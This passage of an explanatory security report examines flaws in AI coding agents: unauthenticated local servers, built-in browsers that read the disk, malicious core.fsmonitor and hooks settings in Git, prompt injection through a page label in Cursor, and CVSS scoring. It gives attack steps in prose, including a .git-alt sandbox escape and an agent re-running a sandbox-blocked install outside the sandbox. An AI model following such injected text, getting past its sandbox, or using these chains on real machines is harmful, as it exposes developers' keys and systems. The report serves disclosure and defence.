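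Anthropic fixed the flaw two months after the report by delaying all requests until the user accepts the trust dialog. MITRE's *Claude Code Leaks Data via Malicious Environment Configuration Before Trust Confirmation* (2026) lists 2.0.65 as the fixed version and 5.3 as the severity score. The fix, as described, does not stop a project from choosing the server, so a developer who trusts a malicious project would presumably still send the key to that server.

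### Comparing the defences

The table shows how four defences would have worked against these leaks. The network column assumes that network limits apply to the entire program, including its chat window and built-in tools.

| Leak | Block remote images | Restrict domains | Restrict network access | Keep secrets out of reach |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot Chat images, 2024 | Yes | Yes | Yes | Not for text already in the chat |
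| Cursor diagrams | Only if the block covers diagrams | Only if the list covers diagrams | Yes | For keys, but not stored memories |
| CamoLeak | Yes | No | No | Yes, if Copilot cannot open other private repositories |
| Claude Code name lookups | No | Only if the list covers lookups | Only if the limits cover lookups | Yes |
| Claude Code domain check | No | Only with a correct check | Yes | Yes |
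| Claude Code and Hugging Face | No | Only if the list excludes the site | Only if the limits exclude the site | Yes |
| Claude Code's redirected API key | No | Only if the list covers the agent's own requests | Yes | No |

Blocking remote images inconveniences users the least, because conversations about code seldom need pictures from other websites. Google's Gemini also does not display external images, according to Checkmarx. The block has to cover every format that can load an image, including diagrams. Ordinary links would remain, and they can still leak data if the user clicks them. Showing a warning with the full address would help, but it adds another prompt that users may ignore.

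Limiting the agent to approved domains lets it read familiar documentation without interruptions. This works poorly for sites such as GitHub, which developers can hardly avoid but where anyone can publish. Trail of Bits' *Prompt injection engineering for attackers* (2025) found that Copilot's cloud agent allows GitHub's content hosts by default. Approving individual pages instead of whole sites would be safer, but it would require maintaining a longer list, and the agent would ask for permission more often.

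Network restrictions stop more of the leaks but interfere more with normal work. Agents need the network to install packages, read documentation and upload code, and most need it to reach the model. Claude Code's sandbox, which covers only shell commands, could have blocked the name lookups but not WebFetch or the requests carrying the API key. Local ports and built-in browsers need their own limits. None of these limits would have helped against CamoLeak, where the user's browser contacted only GitHub.

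Keeping secrets out of the agent's reach is the best protection against unanticipated leaks, because it works whichever route the data would have taken. Developers can block access to password files and give the agent test accounts with few permissions, but the agent then can't run programs or tests that need the real credentials, so the developer has to run them separately. Limiting Copilot to one repository would also prevent it from answering questions that depend on code in another.

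Some secrets have to remain available. Claude Code needs a key or another form of login to contact Anthropic, so hiding the project's password files would not have prevented CVE-2026-21852. Automated build systems often need keys to publish software. *클로드 코드 원격실행 결함, 앤트로픽 “설계대로” 해명* (송, 2026) reports that Novee demonstrated leaks of such secrets in August 2026, using only a pull request or a GitHub issue. In both cases, a key that expires quickly and has few permissions limits the damage.

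Developers can also overlook copies of a secret. When a user tells Claude Code not to ask about a command again, it saves the command, including any password or key it contains, in a local settings file. The Hacker News' *Claude Code's “Don't Ask Again” File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026) reports that the security company Apiiro found 2,539 credentials exposed this way in 1,994 public GitHub repositories. Legit Security found the settings file in almost one in 100 of the 154,420 VS Code extensions it examined. Blocking the agent's access to `.env` would not protect a key that also appears in the settings file.

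## How did local servers and built-in browsers expose developers?

Most attacks on coding agents start with text or files that the agent reads, but others start with a web page that the developer opens. The page may be able to connect to a small server that the coding tool runs on the developer's machine. It may also open in the tool's built-in browser and be able to do things that an ordinary browser would block.

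### Why coding tools run local servers

If a developer selects code in an editor and asks an agent in a terminal to explain it, the agent has to get the selected lines from the editor. The two are separate programs, so one of them usually acts as a server. It opens a port, which is a numbered connection point, and waits for the other to connect.

Such a server normally listens on localhost (127.0.0.1), which other machines can't reach. But scripts in a web page run in the developer's browser, on the same machine, and can open connections to localhost. A firewall between the machine and the internet doesn't block these connections because they stay on the machine. A page that doesn't know the port number can try many. Some browsers now ask the user before letting a public website contact a local program, but a tool's developers can't count on every browser doing so.

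Browsers keep websites apart with the same-origin policy, which dates from 1995. The University of Washington explains that this policy lets a person have an unsafe site open in one tab and a bank account in another without the first site reaching the second. An origin is the combination of a site's protocol, hostname and port. For an ordinary web request, the browser stops a page from reading another origin's reply unless that origin allows it. The request may still reach the server, though, and can do harm if the server acts on it.

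A WebSocket is a connection that stays open so that both sides can send messages at any time. SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-52882* notes that WebSocket connections can get around the same-origin policy if the server doesn't check where they come from. The browser starts each connection with an Origin header naming the site whose page opened it, and scripts on that page can't change the header. The server has to read the header and refuse connections from sites it doesn't know.

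An origin check stops web pages, but any other program on the machine can set the Origin header to any value. An authentication token is stronger. The server creates a long random secret when it starts, saves it in a file that only the user's account can read, and refuses any connection that doesn't include the secret. The agent can read the file because it runs under the user's account, but a web page in an ordinary browser or another person with an account on the same computer can't. Malware already running as the user could read the token, though it could usually read the user's other files too.

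### Claude Code's editor extensions

The first advisory that Anthropic published for Claude Code, in June 2025, concerned a server with neither protection. Claude Code has extensions for VS Code and for JetBrains editors that connect the terminal agent to the editor. In CVE-2025-52882, a website could use the same connection:

1. The developer opens an editor with the extension installed, and the extension starts a WebSocket server on the machine.
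2. The developer visits the attacker's page in any browser. The developer doesn't have to open a malicious project, and no model has to follow planted text.
3. A script in the page connects to the server. The browser names the attacker's site in the Origin header, but the extension accepts connections from any origin and asks for no token.
4. The page sends requests as if it were Claude Code.

Tenable's *CVE-2025-52882* reports that in VS Code and editors based on it, such as Cursor and Windsurf, the page could then read any file, list the open files, and track the developer's selections and the errors the editor reported. The page could run code only if the developer had a Jupyter notebook (a document containing runnable code) open and accepted a malicious prompt.

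Datadog Security Labs' *CVE-2025-52882* (2025) calls the flaw critical and emphasises that an attacker could run commands. Given those two conditions, file theft was the more realistic danger. OSV's *CVE-2025-52882* (2025) lists a score of 8.8, which is high rather than critical. That score is based on an attack over the network, although the server was local, with the visit to the page as the user's part in the attack.

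SentinelOne dates Anthropic's patch to June 13, ten days before the advisory. The vulnerability affected versions 0.2.116 to 1.0.23 of the VS Code extension and 0.1.1 to 0.1.8 of the JetBrains plugin. vuln.today's *CVE-2025-52882* advises users to update to 1.0.24 (VS Code) or 0.1.9 (JetBrains) and restart the editor. Without a restart, the old server may still be open. Datadog Security Labs reports that the vulnerable versions are no longer in the extension stores.

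The public descriptions leave it unclear which protection Anthropic added. OffSeq's *CVE-2025-52882* classifies the flaw as CWE-1385, missing origin validation in WebSockets, and the title in GCVE's *CVE-2025-52882* (2025) mentions "arbitrary origins", while Datadog Security Labs describes the server as unauthenticated. An origin check alone would have blocked the hostile page, but a token would also have kept out other users of the same computer.

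### OpenCode and Cursor's cloud agents

OpenCode also ran a local server without authentication (CVE-2026-22812). Because the server used HTTP instead of WebSockets, the same-origin policy could have given some protection. But the server had permissive cross-origin resource sharing (CORS) settings, which tell browsers which other sites may use it. According to the CVE's published description, any website could therefore run shell commands on the developer's machine, and so could any program already running there.

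Cursor had this problem in its Cloud Agent, which works on a project in a remote container instead of on the developer's machine. In some sessions, the agent had a browser. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-61613* describes how a page in that browser could reach the agent's software in the same container through an endpoint that required no authentication. The page could then run code in the container and read the session's files, environment variables and credentials.

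The container kept this code away from the developer's own disk, but the credentials included GitHub access tokens, which an attacker could use from elsewhere while they remained valid. Cursor fixed the flaw on March 31, 2026, by requiring authentication. The record gives a date instead of a version number, presumably because Cursor runs the service itself and could update it for everyone at once.

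That endpoint's developers may have assumed that only the agent's own software could reach it from inside the container. Adding a browser made that assumption false, because a browser runs scripts from untrusted websites. Sandboxed agents had reached the home folder through the Docker service, which also trusted any program that could connect to it.

### Five built-in browsers

Many coding tools now include a browser that the agent can use to show a preview of a web app, read documentation or click through an interface. On October 29, 2026, the company Forever Security published flaws in five of these tools under the name EMBRACE. According to Spcnet.it's *EMBRACE* (2026), the name stands for "EMbedded BRowser, trusted like a real one".

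*Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (Zorz, 2026) describes how researchers tested the built-in browsers against three rules that ordinary browsers enforce: a page can't run commands on the computer, a local file can't read the user's other files, and only the browser controls what the address bar shows. Ordinary browsers treat every page as hostile, but vendors had relaxed their built-in browsers so that the agent could preview a local project or read a tab's contents. In each product, one of the three rules failed.

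| Product | What a page could do | Forever Security's report | Status at the end of October 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | Read any of the user's files | July 27 | No fix |
| VS Code | Read any of the user's files | September 10 | Microsoft declined the report; no fix |
| Claude Desktop | Read any of the user's files | July 23 | Anthropic declined this report but accepted another; no confirmed fix |
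| Cursor | Pass a command to the agent | September 10 | Fixed on October 1 |
| GitHub Copilot | Show a false address | None before the fix | Fixed on October 13 in version 1.1.29 |

### One local page, the whole disk

In Codex, VS Code and Claude Desktop, the attack starts with a project that looks like an ordinary financial report. The developer asks the assistant to set it up as the README describes. The assistant replies with a link to an HTML file in the project, and the developer clicks it. The file opens in the built-in browser, and its script starts reading the disk with nothing visible on the screen.

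Cornelißen (2026), in *Eingebaute Browser in KI-Tools angreifbar*, points out that developers are more inclined to trust the link because they trust the assistant. The assistant doesn't have to do anything unusual, since many projects have a page to open after installation.

Codex had no folder limit, so a script in a local page could request any file by its path. VS Code and Claude Desktop limited local pages to the project folder, but they didn't apply the limit to requests from web workers, which are scripts that a page can start in the background. Claude Code similarly left one route to the disk less protected when it checked file edits more strictly than shell commands.

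The script also needs a way to find files. On a Mac, it can map the disk one folder at a time by reading the hidden index files that the system leaves in each folder a user has opened in Finder. On the researchers' own machine, it collected SSH keys (used to log in to other computers), `.env` files and npm tokens, and sent them to an outside server. The script could contact that server directly, so the attacker didn't need to hide the data in an image address for a chat window to load. A sandbox that covers only shell commands wouldn't stop this, because the browser reads the files.

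### Does trusting the folder settle the matter?

Microsoft and Anthropic declined Forever Security's reports because the user had already accepted the workspace trust dialog. Their reasoning has some merit, since a trusted folder's contents may run code, and code running as the user can read the same files without a browser.

Gal Weizman, who wrote up the research, told Zorz that the dialog "provides zero protection to the user". Weizman argued that developers accept it every time because the tool is useless in an untrusted project.

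A better argument against the vendors is that VS Code and Claude Desktop both restricted local pages to the project folder even after the user had trusted it, so their developers evidently thought that trust shouldn't give a page access to the whole disk. The web worker bypassed that restriction. Trusting a project also doesn't normally let the agent run arbitrary commands without approval, but here clicking a link was enough to leak the user's keys.

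Anthropic's decisions were also inconsistent. It rejected Forever Security's July 23 report but accepted one that Noma Security filed a day later. Cornelißen describes the two reports as equivalent. Neither Anthropic nor the researchers have said whether a fix exists or which version contains it.

OpenAI had not answered the researchers by the time they published. Cornelißen checked the release notes for VS Code 1.144.0 and Codex 0.166.0, which came out on October 28 and 29, and found no matching fix in either. Forever Security sells monitoring for AI agents, so the report is also advertising, as Cornelißen notes, but its technical steps are detailed enough to follow.

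### A page that writes to the agent, and a false address

Cursor's browser let any website put content into the box where the developer writes to the agent. The researchers' page showed a harmless-looking label, "Start setup", that hid instructions for the agent. The agent responded to these by asking to run a command that would install an npm package. The developer only had to press Enter. The package's installation script then opened the calculator, but it could have started any program with the developer's privileges.

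Cursor's sandbox blocked the installation at first. The agent then ran the command again without the sandbox, although the page contained no instruction to do so. The attack took one press of Enter, so the developer apparently didn't get a chance to refuse the second attempt. It didn't work with every model, so some developers may have been safe because of the model they chose. Cursor fixed the flaw three weeks after the report, without replying to the researchers or publishing an advisory.

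The Copilot flaw affected the browser preview in GitHub's Copilot app. The app accepted the address a page reported for itself, checking only that the text looked like a web address, not that it matched the page the app had loaded. A fake login form could therefore appear under `github.com/login`. The app also passed the false address to the agent, so asking the agent whether the page was genuine would have been little help. The researchers confirmed the flaw in version 1.1.27 on September 26, but GitHub fixed it independently before the researchers reported it.

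Until the remaining flaws are fixed, Cornelißen recommends logging in to websites only in an ordinary browser and not opening unfamiliar local pages in the built-in one. The second precaution is easy to forget when the agent supplies the link.

### Other routes between the browser and the agent

Flaws in the software underneath a built-in browser can also put developers at risk. OX Security counted at least 94 known vulnerabilities in the components beneath Cursor's Simple Browser. In its demonstration, a victim clicked a link that opened Cursor with a ready-made prompt, and the prompt sent the browser to the attacker's page. Scanning the prompt would not have revealed the malicious code, because it was on the page. The demonstration only crashed the browser. OX Security argues that an attacker could use the same kind of memory error to run code, which is plausible but harder.

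Knostic, another security company, described an MCP server that hijacked Cursor's built-in browser. The developer must first install the malicious server, which can already run as a program on the machine. Hijacking the browser also lets the server act on web pages, such as one where the developer enters a password.

Authentication doesn't help if the attacker controls a page that the tool is meant to trust. Claude Dispatch let people send work from a phone or browser to Claude Desktop on their computer. In *ThisBash Escape* (November 2026), Weizman showed that any browser extension able to control the claude.ai website could use Dispatch to run code on that computer. The extension could be on a different machine signed in to the same Claude account, so a malicious extension on a home computer could reach an employer's laptop.

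An origin check would have accepted these requests because they came from the real website and the user had already logged in. Anthropic is retiring Dispatch, but Weizman notes that Claude Code's Remote Control feature also lets a website direct an agent on the user's machine. Asking for approval on the computer that will run the command would be a partial remedy, because a browser extension on another machine couldn't respond to the prompt. It would also make sending work to an unattended computer much less convenient.

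## Why did one Git setting run attackers' commands in seven agents?

Coding agents start Git in the background. Git is the program most developers use to track changes to their code, and its `core.fsmonitor` setting can make routine Git commands run an attacker's program.

Git normally finds changed files by scanning the project. To save time, the `core.fsmonitor` setting lets a developer name a helper program that reports the changes instead. The setting's value is a command, which Git runs whenever it needs to know what has changed. Sonar, a company that makes code-checking tools, notes that `git status` and `git diff` both run the command. Git reads the setting from the project's own `.git/config` file, so anyone who prepares that file can choose the command.

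An agent needs to know which branch the developer is on and which files have changed, so it runs these Git commands soon after it opens a folder. The agent's own code starts Git without a request from the model, so there is no tool call to check, and the attacker doesn't need prompt injection. The helper runs outside the sandbox with the user's privileges, and no approval prompt appears.

Manifold Security published this attack on September 1, 2026, under the name GitSpawn. Its researcher, Francisco Rosales, reported eight flaws in seven agents.

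### Why a zip file is riskier than a clone

The attack works only if the project reaches the developer with its `.git` folder intact. `git clone`, the usual way to download a project, copies the files and their history but creates a new `.git/config` on the developer's machine. Neither cloning nor later fetches and pulls copy the attacker's setting.

A zip file, shared drive, synced folder or USB stick can carry the whole `.git` folder, including its settings. Every demonstration in Manifold's post used a zip file, according to *Opening the Folder Was the Exploit* (paddo, 2026). An archive of the source files alone, without `.git`, can't carry the setting.

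Digital Matters' *GitSpawn* (2026) points out that this is the opposite of what many developers expect. They are wary of cloning an unknown project but may accept a folder from a client or a previous developer without hesitation. Web agencies often inherit old sites this way. Still, the condition rules out the easiest attack, in which someone publishes a malicious project and waits for strangers to clone it.

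### Eight flaws and their fixes

The table combines the versions in The Hacker News' *Malicious .git Configs Can Make Claude, Codex, Cursor, and Other AI Agents* (2026) with later reports. Alibaba makes Qwen Code, xAI makes Grok Build, and Nous Research makes Hermes Agent. The seventh agent, goose, is open source.

| Agent | Vulnerable versions | Latest reported status |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, at startup | Confirmed in 2.1.193 | Fixed by 2.1.196 |
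| Claude Code, `ultrareview` command | Confirmed in 2.1.252 | Unresolved on September 28 |
| Codex CLI (CVE-2026-19592) | 0.102.0 to 0.130.0 | Fixed in 0.131.0 |
| Cursor | Not listed | Fixed, with no advisory found |
| goose (CVE-2026-72718) | Before 1.44.0 | Fixed in 1.44.0 |
| Hermes Agent (CVE-2026-71963) | 0.18.2 to 0.21.0 | Fix merged on September 2 |
| Qwen Code | Confirmed in 0.19.6 and 0.22.3 | Unfixed on September 1 |
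| Grok Build | Confirmed in 0.2.93 and 1.0.13 | Unfixed on September 1 |

Four flaws were still exploitable when Manifold retested them on September 1: the second one in Claude Code and those in Hermes Agent, Qwen Code and Grok Build. Vendors had closed five of Rosales's eight reports as duplicates of ones they already had.

In Claude Code, the helper ran before the user accepted the trust dialog; in Qwen Code, before the user logged in; and in Grok Build, at the first keystroke. In goose, it ran only when the user ran `goose review`, which called `git diff` to collect the changes for review. OSV's *CVE-2026-72718* (2026) notes that this happened before goose contacted a model. Goose overrode one Git setting, which controls how Git prints unusual file names, but not `core.fsmonitor`.

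Hermes Agent's developers merged a fix the day after Manifold's post, but HOL's *CVE-2026-71963* warns that version 0.21.0, the newest release when HOL published, does not include it. One of the two version ranges in OSV's *CVE-2026-71963* lists 0.21.0 as fixed, which could mislead readers. VulnCheck's *Hermes Agent 0.18.2* describes the helper as running once the user sends a message, while HOL describes it as running before the first prompt.

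### A flaw that editors had already fixed

Code editors also run Git when a folder opens, and some had the same flaw years earlier. Nizry's *Arbitrary code execution and Claude Code CLI* lists CVE-2021-43891, which affected VS Code before version 1.63.1, and CVE-2022-24346, which affected JetBrains editors before 2021.3.1. Microsoft's fix kept VS Code from running Git until the user trusted the workspace.

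Justin Steven's 2022 advisory, *Git honours embedded bare repos, and exploitation via core.fsmonitor*, demonstrated the problem in several editors, including GitHub's Atom, which reportedly was not going to get a fix. According to grith's *A Git Config Key Ran Code in Seven Coding Agents*, Steven also recorded that Git's developers had no plans to change how Git treats dangerous settings in a project. Programs that run Git therefore have to guard against those settings.

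Some newer editors didn't wait for the user to trust a folder before running Git. Until version 0.227.1, Zed ran the helper even when the user had opened the folder in untrusted mode, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-44465* (2026). The Eclipse Foundation's *[Eclipse Theia] Arbitrary code execution via untrusted git repository configuration* describes a similar flaw in Theia, a framework for building editors, which started Git without first asking the user to trust the folder.

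### How the flaw returned to Claude Code

Claude Code originally ran `git status` before showing its trust dialog. Version 2.0.34, released on November 5, 2025, stopped doing so, but Nizry, a researcher at Sonar, found that version 2.0.50 still ran five other Git commands before the dialog. Nizry then looked for another setting that would make one of those commands start a program.

Two attempts failed. One relied on a separate program that Git can use to display long output, but Git does this only in an interactive terminal, and Claude Code captured the output instead. The other relied on an outside program that Git can use to compare files, but `git log` doesn't use one unless the command asks for it.

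The third attempt worked. One setting made `git log` verify the digital signatures on saved changes, and another named the program that verified them. The project needed at least one signed change, which an attacker could get by starting from an existing project.

Anthropic fixed this in version 2.0.71, along with a related flaw in which Claude Code ran commands from a project's `.claude/settings.json` before the user answered the trust dialog. Nizry's claim that cloning a malicious project was enough for an attack is true of the settings file, which Git can copy like any other project file, but not of `.git/config`.

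Manifold found the original startup behaviour again in version 2.1.193, released on June 25, 2026. Anthropic had fixed it by 2.1.196, and the published accounts don't explain why it came back. paddo suggests a general cause: Anthropic removes dangerous settings from individual Git commands instead of blocking Git until the user trusts the folder. Each new feature that runs Git then needs the same protection.

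The second flaw fits that explanation. It affects `claude ultrareview`, a cloud code-review command that Anthropic added in version 2.1.111, after the fix for Nizry's findings. The command failed to remove a different Git setting, which Manifold has not named, and the attacker's program could run before the user accepted the trust dialog.

Outside checks of later versions are incomplete. paddo tried the startup attack on version 2.1.259 with a harmless script, and the script did not run, at least in the mode where Claude Code answers one prompt and exits. grith, which sells a security tool for agents, searched the program files of three versions from 2.1.263 onward and found text that turns off `core.fsmonitor` and Git hooks. It concluded that Anthropic had closed the second path between 2.1.252 and 2.1.263.

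That conclusion is too strong, because the overrides may not cover the unnamed setting. A text search also can't show that every Git command uses the overrides. grith found no override text in a recent version of Codex, although OpenAI had fixed the flaw there. On September 28, Digital Matters still described the second Claude Code path as unresolved.

### Three Git settings in Codex

On the day Manifold published, OpenAI released records for three Git flaws in Codex, which it credited to three unrelated groups of researchers. Each flaw used a different setting in `.git/config`:

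- **`core.fsmonitor`:** OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-19592* (2026) covers both the command-line tool and the desktop app. Codex collected information about a project without turning the setting off.
- **`core.hooksPath`:** Git hooks are programs that Git runs at set moments, such as before it saves a change. This setting tells Git which folder holds them. According to OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-19590* (2026), the desktop app's automatic Git commands could run hooks from an attacker's folder.
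- **`attr.tree`:** This setting controls where Git finds rules about how to treat particular files. The rules can assign a filter, which is a program that converts a file's contents. OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-19593* (2026) describes how the desktop app could start an attacker's filter while checking which files had changed.

The last two flaws came from Pwn2Own, and OpenAI received both reports on June 2. Zero Day Initiative's *(Pwn2Own) OpenAI Codex External Control of System or Configuration Setting* (2026) credits the hooks flaw to Sina Kheirkhah of Summoning Team. A second Zero Day Initiative advisory with the same title credits the filter flaw to Satoki Tsuji of Ikotas Labs.

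The Hacker News put OpenAI's three flaws in the same class as Manifold's, which is fair because all of them let a project's Git settings start a program. CVE-2026-19591 has a neighbouring number and came out the same day, but MITRE lists it as the PowerShell parsing flaw.

The severity scores are less consistent. Two of the Git flaws score 7.3, while the filter flaw scores 9.8 on the assumption that the attack needs no action from the victim. But according to OpenAI's own description, the victim must open the attacker's folder, as with the other two.

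### Two Cursor flaws that cloning does not prevent

A hijacked agent can create the dangerous setting itself, so the developer doesn't have to receive a prepared folder. Cursor's sandbox on macOS tried to prevent this by blocking writes to any path ending in `/.git/config`. But Git has a standard option that stores its data in a folder with another name and leaves a small `.git` file pointing there. Cohen (2026), in *The Week of Sandbox Escapes Day 4*, used that option to escape:

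1. The sandboxed agent creates a new repository (a project that Git tracks) inside the workspace and keeps its Git data in a folder called `.git-alt`.
2. The agent sets `core.fsmonitor` in `.git-alt/config` to run a script. The sandbox allows the write because the path doesn't match the blocked pattern.
3. Cursor's Git extension, which runs outside the sandbox, notices the new repository and runs `git status`.
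4. Git runs the script outside the sandbox, without asking the user.

The script opened the calculator, which the sandbox had blocked the agent from opening directly. Cursor had made the same kind of mistake when it checked for only one spelling of its MCP settings file.

Cohen recommends that the sandbox follow the `.git` file to the real settings and protect them wherever they are. The extension should also turn off `core.fsmonitor` while it looks for repositories or, better, ask the user before trusting a new one.

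CVE-2026-26268 concerns Git hooks. VPNCentral's *Cursor AI coding agent flaw lets malicious repositories run code* describes a malicious project that contains a bare repository, which holds Git's data without a working copy of the files. An attacker can store the bare repository as ordinary project files, so `git clone` copies its settings and hooks too. If Cursor's agent then runs a Git command there, Git can run the attacker's hook.

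Enginsight instead says the sandboxed agent writes the Git settings, so there may be two ways to get the same result. Cursor fixed the flaw in version 2.5.

VibecodedThis argues that the cause is the decision to let an agent run Git without knowing whether the project is trustworthy, not a bug in Cursor's code. A person who ran the same command in the same folder could also set off the hook. But Cursor chose to have its agent run Git unprompted, and its fix suggests a vendor can make this safer without changing Git.

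Intruder notes that CVE-2026-55607, the worktree flaw in Claude Code, also used the file-monitor setting. In July, The Hacker News (2026) reported that Cursor could run an attacker's own version of Git, planted in a project as `git.exe`.

### Turning the setting off

grith ran `git status` in three ways on a project whose `core.fsmonitor` setting contained a harmless command. With Git's normal settings, the command ran. It also ran with `safe.bareRepository`, an optional protection from 2022 that Steven recommended. That protection makes Git refuse bare repositories hidden inside a project, so it could help against the attack VPNCentral describes, but it doesn't affect an ordinary repository with a malicious setting. When grith blanked `core.fsmonitor` on the command line, the command did not run.

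The override has to be on the command line because a project's settings take precedence over the developer's global ones, as Digital Matters points out. OpenCVE's page for CVE-2026-19592 includes an AI-generated recommendation to blank the setting globally, which would leave the developer exposed.

Manifold advises agent makers to clean up Git's settings for every background command, according to Expert Insights' *Hackers can get Claude Code, Cursor and other AI agents to hack*. This can take many changes. Hermes Agent's fix overrides the file monitor, hooks, login helpers, and the programs Git uses to display and edit text. Commands that show differences between files need two more options, and the developers' tests found that each option blocks a route the other leaves open. With all these changes, the fix blocked all ten automatic routes the developers tested.

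An agent that waits for the user to trust the folder, as VS Code does, doesn't need a list of every dangerous setting. But waiting doesn't protect the user after they accept, and a developer who received the folder from a client will probably accept. An agent can avoid running Git commands until the user accepts, and override the known dangerous settings afterwards.

For settings that both measures miss, grith's product supervises every process the agent starts, including Git and its helper. In the company's own test, the product stopped the helper for review when it tried to read a decoy login key.

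Until their agent has a fix, developers can inspect `.git/config` before opening a project they received as files. HOL warns that a search for known dangerous settings may miss others, and recommends a fresh clone from a trusted source instead. It also advises anyone who has already opened such a project in a vulnerable version of Hermes Agent to replace their AI service keys.

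## How severe are these flaws, and who decides?

CISA gave one of the Git flaws in Codex a severity score of 7.3 and another a score of 9.8, although the two attacks need similar conditions. Under CVSS, a formula calculates the score from a person's answers to fixed questions, so disagreements over scores come from different answers.

### The CVSS 3.1 formula

Version 3.1 has eight questions. Four cover how hard the attack is: where it can be launched from, how complex it is, what privileges the attacker needs and whether another person has to do something. Three cover harm to confidentiality, integrity (whether the attacker can change data) and availability. The last, called scope, is whether the harm reaches beyond the part of the system that the flawed software controls.

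FIRST, an association of security teams, maintains the system. FIRST's *CVSS v3.1 Specification Document* gives each answer a weight. These are the ones needed here:

| Question | Weights |
|---|---|
| Attack vector | Network 0.85, local 0.55 |
| Attack complexity | Low 0.77, high 0.44 |
| Privileges required | None 0.85, low 0.62 |
| User interaction | None 0.85, required 0.62 |
| Confidentiality, integrity and availability (one weight each) | High 0.56, low 0.22, none 0 |

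If the scope is unchanged, the calculation has four steps, where C, I and A are the weights for the three kinds of harm:

1. Impact base = 1 − (1 − C) × (1 − I) × (1 − A)
2. Impact = 6.42 × impact base
3. Exploitability = 8.22 × vector × complexity × privileges × interaction
4. Score = impact + exploitability, with a maximum of 10, rounded up to one decimal place

Microsoft rated CVE-2025-53773, which let Copilot turn off its own approval prompts, as requiring local access, low complexity, no privileges and user interaction, with high impact on confidentiality, integrity and availability. The impact base is 1 − 0.44 × 0.44 × 0.44, or about 0.915, which gives an impact score of 5.87. The exploitability score is 8.22 × 0.55 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62, or 1.83. The two scores add up to 7.71, which rounds up to 7.8. GCVE's *CVE-2025-53773* (2025) lists impact as 5.9 and exploitability as 1.8.

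For a changed scope, NVD's *CVSS v3.1 Equations* replaces step 2 with 7.52 × (impact base − 0.029) − 3.25 × (impact base − 0.02)^15, and multiplies the sum in step 4 by 1.08. With the other answers the same as Microsoft's, the possible scores are:

| Attack vector | User interaction | Scope unchanged | Scope changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Local | Required | 7.8 | 8.6 |
| Network | Required | 8.8 | 9.6 |
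| Network | None | 9.8 | 10.0 |

CVSS scores from 7.0 to 8.9 count as high and those from 9.0 as critical, so changing the answer to one scoring question can move a flaw into the top category. NIST (2022) noted that there was no ground truth on which to base the weights in the scoring equations, and that FIRST's experts maintain the equations using their own judgment. A score of 9.8 therefore reflects expert opinion about severity and doesn't measure expected damage.

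### Why planted text makes the answers arguable

Under FIRST's specification, the attack vector is local if the attacker relies on another person to open a malicious document. A downloaded project with instructions hidden in its README fits that description. But "network" seems more accurate when an agent fetches planted text from a web page or a GitHub issue without anyone opening a file from the attacker.

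Microsoft scored the Copilot flaw 7.8, and CISA scored CVE-2026-19591, in which Codex misread a PowerShell marker, 8.8. The scores differ only because Microsoft rated the attack vector "local" and CISA rated it "network". These ratings should arguably be swapped, since the Copilot attack could start from a web page, while the Codex attack needs the developer to open a project that the attacker prepared.

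For an attack to work, somebody has to use the agent, but often only to ask an ordinary question. CVSS version 3.1 allows only two ratings for user interaction, "required" and "none". Version 4.0, published in 2023, divides "required" into passive interaction, such as normal use of the program, and active interaction, such as deliberately accepting a warning. Passive suits most prompt injections, though active fits better if the victim must approve a command.

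A sandbox escape is a good candidate for changed scope, because the attacker starts in a confined process and can then affect the rest of the machine. The case is weaker for a command-check flaw, because the agent usually runs with the user's full privileges already and the attacker only avoids an approval prompt. Whether such a prompt is a security boundary is disputed. Cursor, for example, describes its approval modes as "guardrails".

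**Attack complexity** is supposed to be high when success depends on conditions outside the attacker's control. The scores compared below all rate it low, even though a model that usually refuses planted instructions looks like such a condition. This is because FIRST tells scorers to assume that the attacker knows the target's general configuration and default defences, and because an attacker can practise on the same model until the wording works. Changing only this rating to "high" would lower CISA's score for the Codex flaw from 8.8 to 7.5.

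An attacker who plants text in a public issue has no account on the victim's machine, so the natural score for "privileges required" is "none". A scorer who treats the agent's own permissions as the attacker's starting point could still choose "low".

### Six flaws and their scores

Before Anthropic could assign its own CVE numbers, GitHub published the records for flaws in Anthropic's products, with links to Anthropic's advisories. NVD then added its own severity scores for some of them. Other databases, including those of GitLab and the software security company Endor Labs, add more scores.

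| Flaw | Score in the original record | Scores from others |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot, editing its own settings (CVE-2025-53773) | Microsoft: 7.8 (version 3.1) | – |
| Codex, PowerShell marker (CVE-2026-19591) | OpenAI: none | CISA: 8.8 (3.1) |
| Claude Code, command options (CVE-2025-66032) | GitHub: 8.7 (4.0) | NVD: 9.8 (3.1) |
| Claude Code, missing settings file (CVE-2026-25725) | GitHub: 7.7 (4.0) | NVD: 10.0 (3.1) |
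| Claude Code, Zsh file writes (CVE-2026-24053) | GitHub: 7.7 (4.0) | NVD: 6.5, GitLab: 8.8, Endor Labs: 9.8 (all 3.1) |
| Claude Code, symlinks and deny rules (CVE-2025-59829) | GitHub: 2.3 (4.0) | NVD: 6.5 (3.1) |

Some of these gaps come from the change of version. Version 4.0 sorts combinations of answers into groups that experts have ranked, then adjusts the score within the group, rather than using a single formula like the one above. It also replaces the scope question with separate questions about harm to the vulnerable system and to other systems, and adds a question, attack requirements, about whether the attack depends on particular conditions on the target.

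Putting GitHub's answers into the 3.1 formula separates the two causes. The calculation below leaves out the new question because it has no equivalent in 3.1. The first two columns of scores differ because of the version, and the last two differ because of judgment.

| Flaw | GitHub's score under 4.0 | GitHub's answers under 3.1 | NVD's score under 3.1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2025-66032 | 8.7 | 8.8 | 9.8 |
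| CVE-2026-25725 | 7.7 | 8.8 | 10.0 |
| CVE-2026-24053 | 7.7 | 8.8 | 6.5 |
| CVE-2025-59829 | 2.3 | 5.4 | 6.5 |

The CVSS version hardly affects the command-option flaw's score. GCVE's *FKIE_CVE-2025-66032* (2025) shows that GitHub counted passive interaction while NVD counted none, which raises NVD's score by a full point. For the sandbox escape, the version adds 1.1 points, and NVD adds another 1.2 by choosing no interaction and changed scope. Changed scope is easy to defend because the attacker's code leaves a sandbox, but no interaction is harder to defend because the user has to restart Claude Code.

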